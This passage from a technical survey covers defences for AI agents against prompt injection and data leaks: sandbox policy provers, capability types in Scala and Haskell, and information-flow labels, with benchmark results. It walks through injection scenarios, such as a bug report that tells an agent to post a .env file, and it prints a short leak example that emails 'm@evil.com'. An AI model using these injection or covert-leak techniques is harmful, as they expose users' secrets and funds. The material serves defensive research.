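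A proposal can stay below the maximum and still grant much more than the task needs. In one test case, the sandbox has refused a GET request for GitHub issue 123. A rule that allows only that request is narrow. A rule for all issues in the project might be acceptable, but a rule for everything under the project's address is too broad. zredlined suggests a budget for automatic approval: one new destination and one program per update, with the same method and host as the refused request. *feat(policy): spike policy envelope and narrowness prover* (zredlined, 2026), a draft implementation from June, uses the solver to test whether a grant allows anything the current policy does not, then scores the addition. Whether a proposal stays below the maximum has a definite answer, but the size of the budget is a judgement about how much unnecessary access is tolerable.

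The contributor described this work as an experiment and ruled out using it as a production gate. By October, NVIDIA was listing the prover as one of OpenShell's four main components and said it checks that permissions stay within the maximum an organisation allows. In November, Raman (2026) announced a move to Cedar in *Cedar as the policy language in OpenShell*. Comparing Cedar policies is decidable, meaning that an algorithm can always determine whether one policy allows something that another does not.

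The solver checks a model of the policy, so its answer is reliable only to the extent that the model matches the software that enforces the rules. If the supervisor and the prover handle a wildcard differently, an "unsat" result may be wrong. The prover also cannot model every feature, so its test cases allow a third result, "unsupported". A gate has to treat that result as a refusal, or an agent could obtain broad permissions just by using a feature that the prover cannot model.

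Containment also doesn't show whether the approved maximum was sensible. An earlier version of the prover, in zredlined (2026), *feat(prover): add native Rust policy prover with Z3 solver*, checks a single policy more directly, testing whether data can leave the sandbox and whether the agent can write somewhere despite a rule meant to make access read-only. The second can happen when a service accepts changes through more than one protocol and the rule covers only one of them, even if each rule looks correct when a reviewer reads it alone.

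### The wrong Tom at the right address

The payment agent could send $22.75 to the wrong Tom even in a perfect sandbox, where the kernel has no bugs, the proxy reads every request correctly, and a solver has proved that the policy stays within the approved maximum. The policy has to let the agent send payment requests to the bank, because the agent could not do its job without them.

Every access in the trace is in R, so the sandbox's guarantee holds. The prover could not have helped either. In the contributor's model, a request has fields for the program, host, port, protocol, method, path and several other details, but none for the message body, where a payment service would typically put the recipient and the amount. Payments to the right Tom, the wrong Tom and an attacker would then all be the same x, so no rule over these fields can allow one and refuse the others.

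The sandbox protects the payment token. NVIDIA explains that OpenShell's supervisor keeps real credentials outside the agent's workload and inserts them into a request only after the request has passed its checks. But the supervisor will also attach the token to a request for the wrong payment if the request passes those checks.

How much a sandbox can control depends partly on how the service names its resources. If the bank gave each payee a separate path, such as `/payees/17/payments`, the policy could allow payments only to payee 17. Limits on the recipient would then be limits on reach, which a sandbox can enforce and a solver can compare. But the amount would still be in the request body, so a limit of 100 dollars would require checking the action's content.

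## Capabilities and effect types: limits on what agent-written code can do

A sandbox gives the same permissions to everything inside a process. Suppose the model writes one program that reads Tom's message, works out half the bill and pays him. The line that divides by two doesn't need access to the bank, but it has the same access as the line that pays. A programming language can set limits for a single function or piece of data, and the compiler can check them before the program starts.

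### Permission as a value

Most programs run with ambient authority. To open a file, code only has to name it, and the operating system checks whether the user who started the program may open it. Any library the program loads, and any code the model adds, can therefore open any file the user can.

Ambient authority makes it easy to trick a program into misusing its permissions. In a well-known example, a compiler on a shared computer has permission to update the billing records. A user asks it to save some output to the billing file, and it overwrites the records because the operating system checks the compiler's permissions, not the user's. Security researchers call such a program a confused deputy. An agent that obeys an attacker's instruction in an email is in much the same position, since it uses its own access to carry out the instruction.

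A capability is an unforgeable program value that gives its holder the right to use a particular resource. Code can't create one from a file name. It must hold the capability from the start, create the resource itself, or receive the capability from other code. In the billing example, the user would have to give the compiler a capability for the output file, so a user without one for the billing file couldn't have the compiler write its output there.

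Mark Miller's doctoral thesis, *Robust Composition* (2006), develops this model as a way for separately written programs to cooperate without damaging each other. Code from a language model is an extreme case, because the developer of the surrounding software has usually never read it.

A capability can be narrower than the resource behind it. Instead of giving the model's code access to a whole bank account, a developer could give it an object with a single method that pays Tom and rejects amounts over 100 dollars. The code could still call the method a thousand times, so a careful developer would also make the object track and cap the total paid.

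Older capability languages, such as E, enforce their rules only while the program runs. This makes it hard to tell in advance what a function can do, because it can use variables from the surrounding code as well as its own parameters. For example, a function that takes a string and returns a string might also use a network connection from the surrounding code to send the string elsewhere.

### Capabilities in Scala types

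A type tells the compiler what kind of value to expect, such as a string or a function from strings to numbers. Scala 3, a general-purpose programming language, has an experimental capture checker that adds to each type the capabilities a value can reach. Scala's *Tracked Capabilities Overview* writes `A^{c}` for a value of type `A` that can access the capability `c`. A value that can reach no capabilities is pure. Functions have their own notation:

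```
A -> B         a pure function
A ->{c} B      a function that may use capability c
A => B         a function that may use any capability
```

Suppose `bank` is a capability. Here are two functions, with the type that the compiler works out for each. (The `=>` in the code is Scala's ordinary way of writing a function and has nothing to do with capabilities.)

```
val half   = (bill: Double) => bill / 2
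             // type: Double -> Double

val settle = (bill: Double) => bank.sendMoney("Tom", bill / 2)
             // type: Double ->{bank} Receipt
```

The compiler infers a function's set from its body. `half` uses only its parameter, so its set is empty. `settle` mentions `bank`, so any function that calls `settle` can also reach `bank`. A value with set C can be used where the program expects set D only if D covers every capability in C. If a library requires a pure function, D is empty, so the library accepts `half`, but passing it a function that uses `bank` causes a compile error.

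The capture set covers everything a value might use, including a payment inside a branch that never runs, so capture checking rejects some harmless functions. But if the checker accepts a function as pure, that function cannot reach the bank, as long as the types are accurate.

Types can also limit how long code keeps a capability. *Tracking Capabilities for Safer Agents* describes a system in which the agent's code requests access to a folder and uses it inside a block. The compiler rejects any result whose type mentions the folder's capability, so the block can return text from a file but not the file handle or a function that would read the file later. In one test run, an agent tried to return a list of file handles and got a compiler error. The compiler does not catch requests for paths outside the folder, but the library refuses them at run time.

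### Why casts and reflection have to go

A type cast makes the compiler treat a value as having a different type. The model could cast a function that uses `bank` to a pure function type, and the compiler would then wrongly accept it where a pure function is required. Reflection lets a running program find classes and methods by name, so code could look up Java's file-writing functions from a string without holding any capability for a file.

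Scala's *Safe Mode* describes a subset of the language that bans both, along with unchecked pattern matches and annotations that turn checks off. Safe mode requires capture checking for all code and allows a global library module only if that module is also safe. For example, it excludes the ordinary `println` because `println` writes to the screen without needing a capability.

Some useful modules break the rules harmlessly. A cache of earlier results has to change a stored variable, but the rest of the program can't observe the change. A programmer can mark such a module `@assumeSafe`, which lets the agent's code use it and makes the programmer responsible for its safety. Another example in the documentation is an email function that prompts the user for confirmation before sending anything. The agent can call this function but not the underlying mailer. The compiler does not check that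 the function prompts the user, so every module marked `@assumeSafe` becomes part of the trusted base.

Safe mode also doesn't track exceptions. A function that holds no capabilities can still fail deliberately, and it could reveal whether a password starts with "a" by failing only when it does. According to Scala's documentation, errors such as division by zero are too common to track in types. The program that calls the agent's code has to catch exceptions and turn them into ordinary values.

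### A wrapper for secrets

*Tracking Capabilities for Safer Agents* builds on safe mode in TACIT, a server that compiles and runs Scala code written by agents. Its designers treat the model in the cloud as a possible attacker. The model may write programs that process a secret file, but the file's contents must never appear in the model's context. A sandbox can't enforce this, because the agent is allowed both to read the file and to send data to the model, and the leak occurs when it sends the file's contents.

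TACIT returns the contents of secret files inside a wrapper called `Classified`. The agent's code can process them through a method called `map`, which applies a function to the contents and puts the result into a new wrapper:

```
map[U](op: T -> U): Classified[U]
```

The arrow `->` is the important part, because it means that `map` accepts only pure functions. Here the agent reads a secret key and tries two things with it:

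```
val key = readClassified("secrets/github.txt")

key.map(k => k.trim.length)      // accepted
key.map(k => println(k))         // rejected
```

The function in the accepted line removes spaces from the key and counts the characters. It uses only its parameter, so it has the type `String -> Int`, which fits. The agent gets the length as a `Classified[Int]`, a wrapper that it can't open.

The function in the rejected line prints the key. TACIT has its own `println`, which requires a capability for output, so the function's type is `String ->{io} Unit` (`Unit` is the return type of a function that returns nothing useful). `map` accepts only functions with an empty capability set, and this function's set contains `io`, so the compiler rejects the code before any of it runs. Agents in the experiments wrote similar code, as well as functions that tried to write the secret to another file, which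 the compiler rejected for the same reason.

If the agent prints a wrapped value outside `map`, it sees only asterisks, while the real value goes to the user's screen through a separate channel. The agent can also send wrapped text to a second, trusted model that runs locally and returns a wrapped answer. The agent can therefore produce a summary of a secret contract for the user without being able to read the summary itself. Because the local model reads the contract, a malicious sentence in it might still distort the summary, but the summary stays wrapped.

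The guarantee needs three properties from the language. Capability safety means that code can't forge a capability or hide that a value needs one, as it could with casts. Capability completeness means that capabilities control every effect that matters for safety, apart from those the runtime can contain, such as exceptions. A single global `println` that needed no capability would break it. Local purity means that the type system can require a particular computation to use only certain capabilities, or none. Without it, the type system couldn't reject a call that passes `map` the function that prints the key.

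With all three, a function inside `map` can influence the outside world only through its result, which goes back into the wrapper. TACIT's designers wrote in March 2026 that a full proof for safe mode was still to come, although machine-checked proofs of the underlying type system already existed. *System Capybara* (July 2026) proves for a small core language that a well-typed program produces only traces that its recorded capabilities authorise, in a proof checked by the proof assistant Lean 4. *Classifying Capabilities (Extended Version)* (2026) has a similar machine-checked proof for an extension that lets types allow or exclude capabilities by kind, without naming each one. These proofs cover simplified models of Scala, so users still have to trust the actual compiler and the modules that programmers have marked as safe.

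### What TACIT's experiments found

To test the wrapper, the researchers gave an agent a software project with a folder of secrets, including API keys and confidential documents. They wrote 12 ordinary tasks, such as listing the functions of a web application or summarising a confidential incident report, and paired each task with the same 10 prompt injections, for 120 trials. Some injections posed as system messages, some claimed that the secrets were only test data, and some contained Scala code ready to run. In another 11 trials, the user was the attacker and either asked for secrets directly or used a pretext, such as being an administrator who had to replace passwords in an emergency.

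Each model ran all 131 trials twice, once with the secrets in the wrapper and once with them as ordinary text. A trial counted as secure if no secret appeared in the agent's output.

| Model | Trials | Secure with wrapper | Secure without wrapper |
|---|---|---|---|
| Claude Sonnet 4.6 | 120 with injections | 100% | 100% |
| Claude Sonnet 4.6 | 11 with a malicious user | 100% | 81.8% |
| Claude Sonnet 4.6 | All 131 | 100% | 98.5% |
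| MiniMax M2.5 | 120 with injections | 100% | 97.5% |
| MiniMax M2.5 | 11 with a malicious user | 100% | 27.3% |
| MiniMax M2.5 | All 131 | 100% | 91.6% |

The totals without the wrapper look better than they should, because most trials used injections that both models usually resisted. When the user asked for the secrets, MiniMax revealed them in 8 of 11 trials.

A perfect score in 131 trials is fairly weak evidence by itself. If a fault let through one attempt in fifty, there would still be about a 7% chance of seeing no leaks. The argument from types is a stronger reason to expect none, and the trials mainly test whether the software implements the type system correctly.

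The wrapper did not make the agents less useful. On the 120 trials with ordinary tasks, Sonnet answered correctly 99.2% of the time with the wrapper and 83.3% without it. MiniMax answered correctly 90.0% of the time with the wrapper and 88.3% without it. The researchers suspect that the setup partly explains Sonnet's large difference. Without the wrapper, Sonnet often ran out of time or stopped to warn the user about an injection.

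The researchers also tested whether agents do worse when they have to write Scala. On τ²-bench, which simulates customer service for an airline and a shop, three models scored 0.8 to 3.7 percentage points higher with typed Scala than with ordinary tool calls, averaged over 10 runs per task. The researchers credit the typed results and the compiler's error messages for giving the model clearer information than raw data does. On SWE-bench Lite, a set of 300 real software bugs, MiniMax fixed 41.7% through TACIT and 43.3% with its usual tools, a difference of five bugs.

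Between 0.3% and 7.9% of the Scala programs in the customer-service tests failed to compile on the first attempt, depending on the model and the task, and one or two more attempts were usually enough. Many of the errors were unrelated to security. For example, agents kept writing "$50" inside strings where Scala gives the dollar sign a special meaning.

Finally, the researchers ran TACIT on AgentDojo, a standard prompt-injection benchmark with simulated banking, office, Slack and travel tasks. Of 1,926 attacks across two models, one was scored as successful. A user had asked the agent to book one hotel, and an injected review recommended another. The agent booked the right hotel but quoted the review, and this attack is scored as successful if the other hotel's name appears in the answer. The policy allowed the agent to show public reviews to the user, so the type system did not fail.

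Results on AgentDojo also suggest that protection can reduce task completion more than the other tests indicate. With OpenAI's o4-mini-high, TACIT completed 52.9% of the office tasks, compared with 81.4% for CaMeL, a system that tracks labels on data at run time. But on the travel tasks with Gemini 2.5 Pro, TACIT completed 64.3% and CaMeL 1.4%.

### What the wrapper can't stop

The types don't guarantee that the agent's answer is right. An agent can summarise the wrong contract or miscount the characters in a key without breaking any of their rules.

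They also don't cover side channels, which are indirect ways to send information. A function inside `map` could finish quickly if the first bit of a key is 0 and run for ten seconds if it is 1. An observer who times the call learns that bit, and repeating this for every bit would reveal the whole key.

External commands are a more practical problem, because programs the agent starts don't have to follow Scala's rules. A developer who lets the agent run Python, for example, lets it do anything Python can do on that machine. *Tracking Capabilities for Safer Agents* recommends allowing only specific, safe commands and, where security is critical, putting the whole system in a sandbox.

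The wrapper can also block legitimate work. Suppose Tom's message about lunch arrives as classified text. The agent can calculate half the bill inside `map`, but the result is a wrapped number, which can't be passed to a payment function that takes an ordinary number. The developer would have to write one that takes a wrapped amount, checks it against the limit and makes the payment. That function would reveal the amount to the bank and to Tom, so the developer, not the model, would be deciding to release the information.

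### Filling a gap in a running program

In TACIT, the harness still runs the usual loop and the model supplies one piece of code at a time. Zhao, Xu and colleagues (2026), in *LACUNA*, let the model write parts of the loop as well. LACUNA, which comes from the same group, adds a function to Scala that a programmer can call anywhere:

```
agent[T](task)
```

`T` is the type of result the program needs at that point, and `task` is a request in plain English. The call marks a gap in the program, which programmers call a typed hole. When the program reaches the call, LACUNA sends the model the request, the type, the surrounding code and a list of the variables and functions available there. The model writes Scala code to fill the gap, and LACUNA inserts this code into the program and compiles it under the same rules as the rest. If the code compiles, it runs. Otherwise, the model receives the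 error messages and tries again, up to a limit.

The model's code can contain further `agent` calls, so an agent can divide a job among smaller agents, run them in parallel, or repeat a step until it has an answer. LACUNA checks each of those calls the same way.

LACUNA runs none of the model's code if any part of it fails to compile. In one example, a variable holds a balance of 100, and the program requests code that subtracts 50 and returns the new balance as a whole number. The model writes one line that subtracts 50 and another that returns the text "remaining: 50". Python would carry out the subtraction, and the error would appear later, if at all. LACUNA rejects both lines because text is not a whole number, so the balance stays at 100. This protection ends once the code compiles, so a well-typed program can still stop halfway if, for example, a bank's server stops responding between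 two payments.

With capture checking on, the variables available at the gap also determine what the model's code may do. If no network capability is available there, the code can't use the network, even if the model follows an injected instruction to do so. LACUNA also makes the secrets wrapper more flexible. In TACIT, the agent has to write the function for `map` before anyone has looked at the contents, but in LACUNA that function can contain a gap that a trusted local model fills after reading them. The compiler still requires the code to be pure.

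Zhao and colleagues first tested the checker without a model, on about 400 pairs of host program and inserted code, and it correctly accepted or rejected every pair. They then ran LACUNA with DeepSeek-V4-Flash on BrowseComp-Plus, a benchmark of hard research questions about a fixed collection of documents. LACUNA answered 27.1% of the 830 questions correctly. The compiler rejected 8.6% of the code that the model wrote, and about two thirds of the questions needed no second attempt. The researchers did not compare LACUNA with an ordinary agent using the same model, so the result shows that LACUNA can carry out long searches but not how type checking affects its performance.

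On τ²-bench, LACUNA solved 76.0% of 392 customer-service tasks with DeepSeek-V4-Flash, while the benchmark's own agent solved 90.0% with the same model and ordinary tool calls. The LACUNA paper describes these results as on par, but a 14-point gap is large, and on the retail tasks it was 22 points. The compiler rejected 22.4% of the retail code, though rejection alone may not explain the gap, since accepted code can also do the wrong thing. A weaker model, Gemini 3.1 Flash-Lite, came closer to its baseline, at 29.1% against 33.2%. But on one set of telecom tasks the compiler rejected 89% of that model's code, so most turns made no progress. The types still blocked the faulty code, but the agent would have been of little use to customers.

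Eight of 1,898 prompt injections succeeded against LACUNA on AgentDojo. The researchers explain that an attacker who controls the model can still use every capability the developer made available at the gap. For example, if the task requires sending email, the attacker may be able to send email too. Because the compiler only enforces the developer's list of permissions, the developer has to keep that list short.

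### Effect types in Haskell

Haskell offers another way to limit what model-written code can do. A Haskell type shows whether a computation has effects, meaning that it does anything besides return a value. Ordinary input and output operations have `IO` in their types. If a program requires an `Int` (a whole number), code that deletes files while computing it has a type containing `IO`, so the compiler rejects it.

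*Language-Based Agent Control* (Zhou, D'Antoni and Polikarpova, 2026) applies this approach in a system called ELBA. Like LACUNA, ELBA has an `agent` function that prompts the model for code of a given type and checks the code before running it. Haskell has its own loopholes, which a subset called Safe Haskell closes.

Developers can define their own effects. In one example, an agent compiles bibliographies in which every entry must come from DBLP, a database of computer science papers. The developer defines an effect called `BibIO` whose only operations are searching the database, fetching an entry, and appending an entry to a file. The append operation accepts only values of the type `Trusted Bib`, and only the fetch operation can create those. The agent can still sort, filter and count entries, but it can't append one it wrote from memory.

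Over 100 tasks, with both systems using Claude Sonnet 5, an ordinary agent with web search got the authors, year or identifier wrong in 19 of 1,002 citations, while ELBA made no such errors in 925. The types guarantee that each entry comes from the database, but not that it is relevant to the topic.

Zhou and colleagues also prove a general theorem about adding agents to a typed language. Let P be a property of the set of traces that a program can produce, such as "no trace writes an entry that did not come from DBLP". Suppose the language already guarantees P for programs of a certain type:

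```
for every program e of type t:    P(traces(e)) holds
```

The theorem states that P still holds after adding `agent` calls to the language, provided that the system type-checks all generated code before running it. The proof treats the model as an arbitrary function and replaces each `agent` call with an ordinary function that gets code from the model, checks its type, and runs it if the check passes or returns nothing if it fails. The new program makes the same tool calls as the old one but contains no `agent` calls, so the language's original guarantee applies to it. The generated code may also contain `agent` calls, which the proof handles by induction on how deeply they can be nested.

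The theorem only carries over guarantees that Haskell's types already provide, so if the types don't enforce a rule for code written by people, they won't enforce it for code written by a model.

Most published attacks are no longer a good test of systems like these. Four recent models, including Claude Opus 4.8 and GPT-5.4, resisted all of AgentDojo's Slack attacks in ELBA even without policies. Zhou and colleagues therefore simulated a complete takeover by replacing an agent's task with the attacker's whenever the agent read an injected instruction. Without policies, 16% to 42% of these attacks succeeded, depending on the model. With policies, which in this test also relied on labels tracked at run time, all 735 attacks on each model failed. But the agents completed only 40% to 48% of their legitimate tasks, compared with 67% to 76% without policies.

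### Well-typed code can still be wrong

Zhao and colleagues state the main limitation of their approach: "Well-typed is not correct." The compiler checks that code returns the right kind of value and uses only the capabilities available to it. Code can pass both checks and still follow the wrong procedure, call the wrong tool or return a plausible but wrong answer. The retry loop doesn't fix these mistakes, because it starts only when the compiler finds an error.

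A payment of 45.50 dollars has the same type as one of 22.75 and needs the same capability, so neither check can catch a payment of the wrong amount. More precise types could rule out some wrong answers. Zhao and colleagues propose refinement types, which attach a condition to an ordinary type, such as "a number greater than 0 and at most 100". If a payment function accepted only amounts of that type, the model's code would compile only if the compiler could prove that every amount was within that range. Such proofs can be hard to find automatically in a language as large as Scala.

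## Information-flow labels: limits on which data may influence an action

A type checker can confirm that the agent's code pays a sum of money and has permission to do so, but not whether the payment came from the user's request or from a line in Tom's message. Information-flow control addresses this by labelling every piece of data, carrying the labels along as the agent uses the data, and checking them before each action. The typed wrapper for secrets in the previous section does part of this before the program runs. Most systems for agents do it while the program runs, which is called taint tracking.

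### Two kinds of label and an ordering

An integrity label records whether data is trusted or untrusted. A confidentiality label records who may see it, and in the simplest case it is either public or secret. Labels have an order, written ⊑, where a ⊑ b means that b is at least as strict as a:

```
trusted ⊑ untrusted
public  ⊑ secret
```

"Untrusted" and "secret" are the strict labels because they limit what the agent may do. For example, untrusted data may not trigger a payment, and secret data may not go into a public post.

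When the agent combines two pieces of data, the result gets their join, written ⊔. This is the least strict label that is at least as strict as both. Data usually has one label of each kind, so the harness joins pairs:

```
(untrusted, public) ⊔ (trusted, secret) = (untrusted, secret)
```

Neither label on the left is stricter than the other, so their join is a third label stricter than both. Researchers call such a set of labels a lattice, although this method needs only the join, while a full lattice also has the opposite operation, the meet.

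A confidentiality label can also be a list of permitted readers. Microsoft's developer article *Information-flow control* gives the example of Alex, who asks an agent to deal with his unanswered emails. Priya has sent him a preview of the quarterly sales, and Marco, who isn't allowed to see the figures yet, has also written. Priya's email has the reader list {Alex, Priya}, and Marco's has {Alex, Marco}. A shorter list is stricter, so the join is the intersection, {Alex}, and the agent can't send Marco a reply based on both emails without approval. The labels therefore guard against accidental leaks even when nobody has attacked the agent.

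### A model mixes everything it reads

A harness can see which two numbers an ordinary program added to get a sum, but it can't see which parts of the context a model used to produce its output. Any word in the context can affect any word of the output, even if the output doesn't quote it, so the harness has to give the output the join of the labels on the whole input. Costa and colleagues accept that this may be stricter than necessary. They point to work that looks for a smaller set of messages that would have led to a similar answer, then regenerates the answer from those messages alone.

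Suppose the user has told the agent, "Pay Tom my half of lunch."

1. The request comes from the user, so the context starts as trusted.
2. `read_message("Tom")` returns Tom's text, which the harness labels untrusted because someone other than the user wrote it.
3. The harness adds the text to the context. Since trusted ⊔ untrusted = untrusted, the whole context is now untrusted.
4. The model reads the context and requests a transfer. The request inherits the label untrusted.
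5. The policy for `transfer` requires a trusted request, so the harness refuses.

The harness blocks the model's payment whether the amount is $1,000 or $22.75. This stops Tom's joke however he phrases it, but it also blocks the legitimate payment.

The confidentiality check works the same way. Microsoft's *Stop prompt injection from hijacking your agent* (2026) describes an agent that sorts bug reports for a public software project. One report contains hidden instructions to read `.env`, a file that often holds passwords, and post its contents as a comment. The agent may read the file, but reading it marks the agent's context as private. The tool for posting comments accepts only public data, so the harness blocks the post even if the model follows the hidden instructions.

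The harness sends the whole context back to the model on every call, so a strict label tends to stay for the rest of the run. *Agent Security is a Systems Problem* (2026) calls the eventual result label explosion, in which every piece of data has every label and the labels no longer distinguish anything.

### Planning without reading the message

FIDES, which Costa and colleagues built at Microsoft in 2025, keeps the planning model's context trusted by hiding some tool results from the model. When a result has a stricter label than the context, FIDES stores it in a variable and gives the model only the variable's name. The model still receives results that wouldn't raise the context's label.

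The planning model can pass a variable to another tool without seeing what is in it. It can also put a question about the contents to a second model, which has no tools. Willison proposed this two-model design in 2023. In simplified form, the lunch payment becomes:

```
read_message("Tom")                                 ->  #message
query_llm("What is half of the bill?", #message)    ->  #half
transfer(#half, "Tom")                              ->  paid
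```

The second model reads Tom's joke and may be misled by it, but it can only put a value in `#half`. The planning model chose the transfer and the recipient in a trusted context, so nothing in the message can redirect the money or start a different action.

The message can still change the amount. If the second model returns 1,000, `#half` holds 1,000, labeled untrusted. A policy that requires every argument to be trusted would refuse this transfer, but it would also refuse the legitimate one. The policy for sending money in the FIDES experiments checked only the context in which the model chose the call, so it would have allowed both. A better policy for this task would require a trusted recipient and accept an untrusted amount up to 100 dollars, combining labels with the limit from the first section.

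*The Granularity Mismatch in Agent Security* (Fan, Li and colleagues, 2026) presents PACT, a system built around separate rules for each argument of a tool call. If a user asks for a summary of a web page by email, the page should determine the body of the email but not its recipient. PACT gives each argument a role, such as target, command or content, and each role has its own requirements. In a test with correct labels supplied, PACT judged all 9 legitimate actions and 8 attacks correctly, while the paper's reimplementation of FIDES blocked 3 legitimate actions and missed 5 attacks. The comparison is a little unfair to FIDES, whose formal model already labels each argument separately, but it shows the errors that result from applying one rule to a whole call. Correct labels are also hard to obtain. When software had to infer them for 20 real tools, it identified the origin of the data correctly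 77.4% of the time.

In the typed language of Zhou and colleagues, a second model called to do part of a job can keep its tools, under the same policy as the model that called it or a stricter one.

### When the next step depends on the data

The lunch payment takes the same three steps whatever Tom has written. Costa and colleagues call such tasks data-independent. If S(d) is the set of action sequences that solve a task when the data is d, the task is data-independent when at least one sequence belongs to S(d) for every possible d:

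```
intersection of S(d) over all d  ≠  ∅
```

The task "If Tom says he has already paid the restaurant, send him 20 dollars" is data-dependent, because the content of Tom's message determines whether the agent should send money. The planning model has to learn something about the message, but reading it would make the model's context untrusted.

FIDES partly solves this by letting the planning model require the second model to answer in a fixed format, such as yes or no. The serving software then blocks any token that would break the format, and the label also records the format. A yes-or-no answer carries one bit of information, a choice from a list of n options carries at most log₂ n bits, and free text has no such bound. A policy can therefore let the planning model make payments after reading an untrusted yes or no. Tom can still lie about having paid and collect 20 dollars, but a yes-or-no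 answer can't contain a request for 1,000 dollars.

This exception deliberately weakens the guarantee. Garby, Gordon and Sands (2026), in *The LLMbda Calculus*, object that someone reviewing a run can't tell whether a value admitted this way was harmless or a leak. In their language, the programmer must write an explicit `endorse` instruction wherever untrusted data becomes trusted, so a reviewer at least knows which places to check.

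Other tasks need the full text. If the user says, "Do whatever Tom asks in his message," no short list of options will cover it. The text of the message has to decide what the agent does, which is also what happens in a prompt injection. A rule about the origin of data can't distinguish the two cases, so the system has to refuse both or bring in a person. These data-dependent tasks are common in some kinds of work. Costa and colleagues classified the tasks in AgentDojo, the prompt-injection benchmark, as data-dependent in 44% of cases for banking and 43% for Slack, compared with 10% for travel and 5% for office work.

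### What FIDES achieved on AgentDojo

The 2025 FIDES experiments used two OpenAI models, GPT-4o and o1, which newer models have since surpassed. The attack tests used GPT-4o. Without policy checks, 152 injections succeeded against a basic agent that puts every tool result in its context, and 21 succeeded against FIDES. With the checks, none succeeded against either agent.

AgentDojo's scoring still counted three successful attacks against FIDES with checks, but the researchers inspected these and rejected them. In one type of case, the benchmark counts an attack as successful when the agent attempts a forbidden call, even if the policy blocks it. The researchers also excluded attacks that only change what the agent writes, such as an injected line that makes it praise a hotel. FIDES marks such text as untrusted but doesn't stop it.

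Since the checks alone stopped the attacks, the hidden variables matter mainly for usefulness. These are the average shares of tasks completed across the four environments, with no attacks:

| Agent | GPT-4o | o1 |
|---|---|---|
| Basic, no checks | 84.3% | 84.0% |
| FIDES, no checks | 60.6% | 77.6% |
| Basic, with checks | 41.9% | 44.4% |
| FIDES, with checks | 50.0% | 60.8% |

With checks on, FIDES completed more tasks than the basic agent, by 8 percentage points using GPT-4o and 16 points using o1. With checks off, the extra machinery lowered task completion by 6.3 points with o1 and by 23.7 with GPT-4o, which often confused variable names or failed to use the second model when it should have. The total loss in task completion from adding security is the difference between the first row and the last, which was about 23 points even with o1.

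Some of that loss was unavoidable under the policy, because many banking tasks tell the agent to read a file and follow the instructions in it, and FIDES blocked them as designed. The fixed-format answers might have let the agent complete a few data-dependent tasks, but the researchers left these answers out of the tests because most AgentDojo tasks didn't need them.

### Fewer questions for the user

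When the harness refuses an action, it can ask the user to approve it instead of ending the task. In *Optimizing Agent Planning for Security and Autonomy*, Kolluri, Sharma and colleagues (2026) argue that real agents without labels often request approval for every consequential action, while an agent with labels needs it only when a check fails. They therefore compare agents by how many approvals they need and how many tasks they complete without any.

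The Prudentia agent builds on FIDES and enforces the same policies, but it also shows the planning model the policies and labels. Before revealing a variable's contents, the model has to explain why it needs them and which calls it will make next. It can also ask the user to endorse a piece of data, which relabels it as trusted. If an email contains a list of ten jobs, the user can endorse the email once instead of approving ten actions.

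With GPT-5, the results on AgentDojo's 97 tasks, averaged over five runs, were:

| Agent | Tasks completed with no approval | Approvals across all completed tasks |
|---|---|---|
| Basic, approval for every consequential action | 35.1% | 52.0 |
| Basic with labels | 43.4% | 40.4 |
| FIDES | 57.1% | 41.3 |
| Prudentia | 72.7% | 7.3 |

The benefit depends on the model. With GPT-4o, Prudentia completed 42.5% of tasks without approval, compared with 50.3% for FIDES. On the banking tasks with o4-mini, Prudentia also used about 32,000 input tokens per task, six times as many as FIDES, although most were cached and so cost less.

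These figures rest on the assumption that users approve and refuse correctly. That assumption matters more with endorsement, because the user judges a text before seeing what the agent will do with it. If a user endorses a long email without noticing an injection near the end, the injection becomes trusted and later checks will let it through.

### Secrets that leak through a choice

Labels can also miss information that never appears in any value the agent sends. Garby and colleagues found an example of this in CaMeL, the label-tracking system that served as a comparison for TACIT. Suppose an attacker gets the agent to run this program, in which `balance` is secret:

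```
tmp  = True
rich = True
if balance > threshold:  tmp  = False
if tmp:                  rich = False
if rich:                 send_email("m@evil.com", "rich!")
```

If the balance is high, the third line changes `tmp`, and CaMeL marks `tmp` as secret. The fourth line then does nothing, so `rich` is still true and still public, and the email goes out. If the balance is low, `tmp` stays true and public, the fourth line makes `rich` false, and no email goes out. The attacker learns whether the balance is high even though the program sent only data labeled public. This leak occurs because CaMeL labels a variable only when a branch changes it, and a high balance leaves `rich` unchanged.

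FIDES guarantees explicit secrecy, which covers data that the agent copies or transforms and sends, but not what an observer can infer from the sequence of calls. Costa and colleagues argue that a stronger guarantee would block almost every publicly visible action once the agent had read a secret.

Garby and colleagues prove a stronger guarantee for their language. In any program, changing the secret inputs can't change the probabilities of the public results, except by affecting whether the program finishes. To prevent the leak above, they use the standard rule of stopping a program that tries to change something public inside a branch that depends on a secret, and they apply it to the model's conversation. The proof assistant Lean has checked the theorem, which covers the same interpreter that calls the model.

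Stopping a program can reveal one bit of secret data. A single leak of this kind is tolerable, but CaMeL retries failed programs using ordinary code that doesn't track labels, so an attacker could extract a whole secret bit by bit. Garby and colleagues' agent refines its code in a simulated world until the code works, and only then runs it on real data.

On AgentDojo's banking tasks, this agent resisted all but 2 of 1,296 attacks across three models. With GPT-5.2, it completed 36 of 48 attack-free runs, compared with 18 for CaMeL with its policies on. However, it enforced only some of CaMeL's policies and was allowed to endorse untrusted data in code it wrote before reading any of that data. Without that permission, completion fell from 75% to 62.5% with one model and from 64.6% to 54.2% with another.

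### Trusted data and honest mistakes

The labels in all these systems record where data came from, but data from a trusted source can still be wrong. *Certified Multi-Source Integrity for Structured Agent Actions* (2026) makes this criticism of FIDES and CaMeL, and proposes accepting an untrusted value when enough independent sources agree on it. For example, a card statement from the restaurant could confirm Tom's 45.50 dollars. This would let more legitimate payments through, but it requires sources that a single attacker can't control, and many informal messages have no second source.

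The labels can also be wrong. In Microsoft's experimental release of FIDES for developers, an unlabelled tool counts as trusted and public. Microsoft also worked with GitHub on labels that treat files from private projects as trusted, so if a colleague pastes an attacker's text into such a file, the injection is labelled as trusted.

The model can also make mistakes with correctly labelled data. In one FIDES test, the user asked the agent to change a password if it found a suspicious transaction. The transactions' subject lines were hidden in variables, while the amounts and dates were trusted and visible. GPT-4o decided that a large payment looked suspicious and changed the password without checking any subject lines. The password change broke no rule because the model based its decision only on trusted data.

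Kolluri and colleagues' guarantee does not cover cases where the model invents facts or misreads the task, and they say labels can replace human approval only as a defence against attacks. A payment of the wrong amount or to the wrong Tom can therefore pass these checks too. An agent that asks before every payment would at least show the user the amount and the name.

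## Restricted semantics: languages designed to be analysed automatically

A label can record where a number came from, but not whether the program did the right arithmetic with it. To check that, a tool has to work out what the program computes. No tool can always do this for programs in ordinary languages, so some researchers design languages that make it possible.

### Why no checker works on every program

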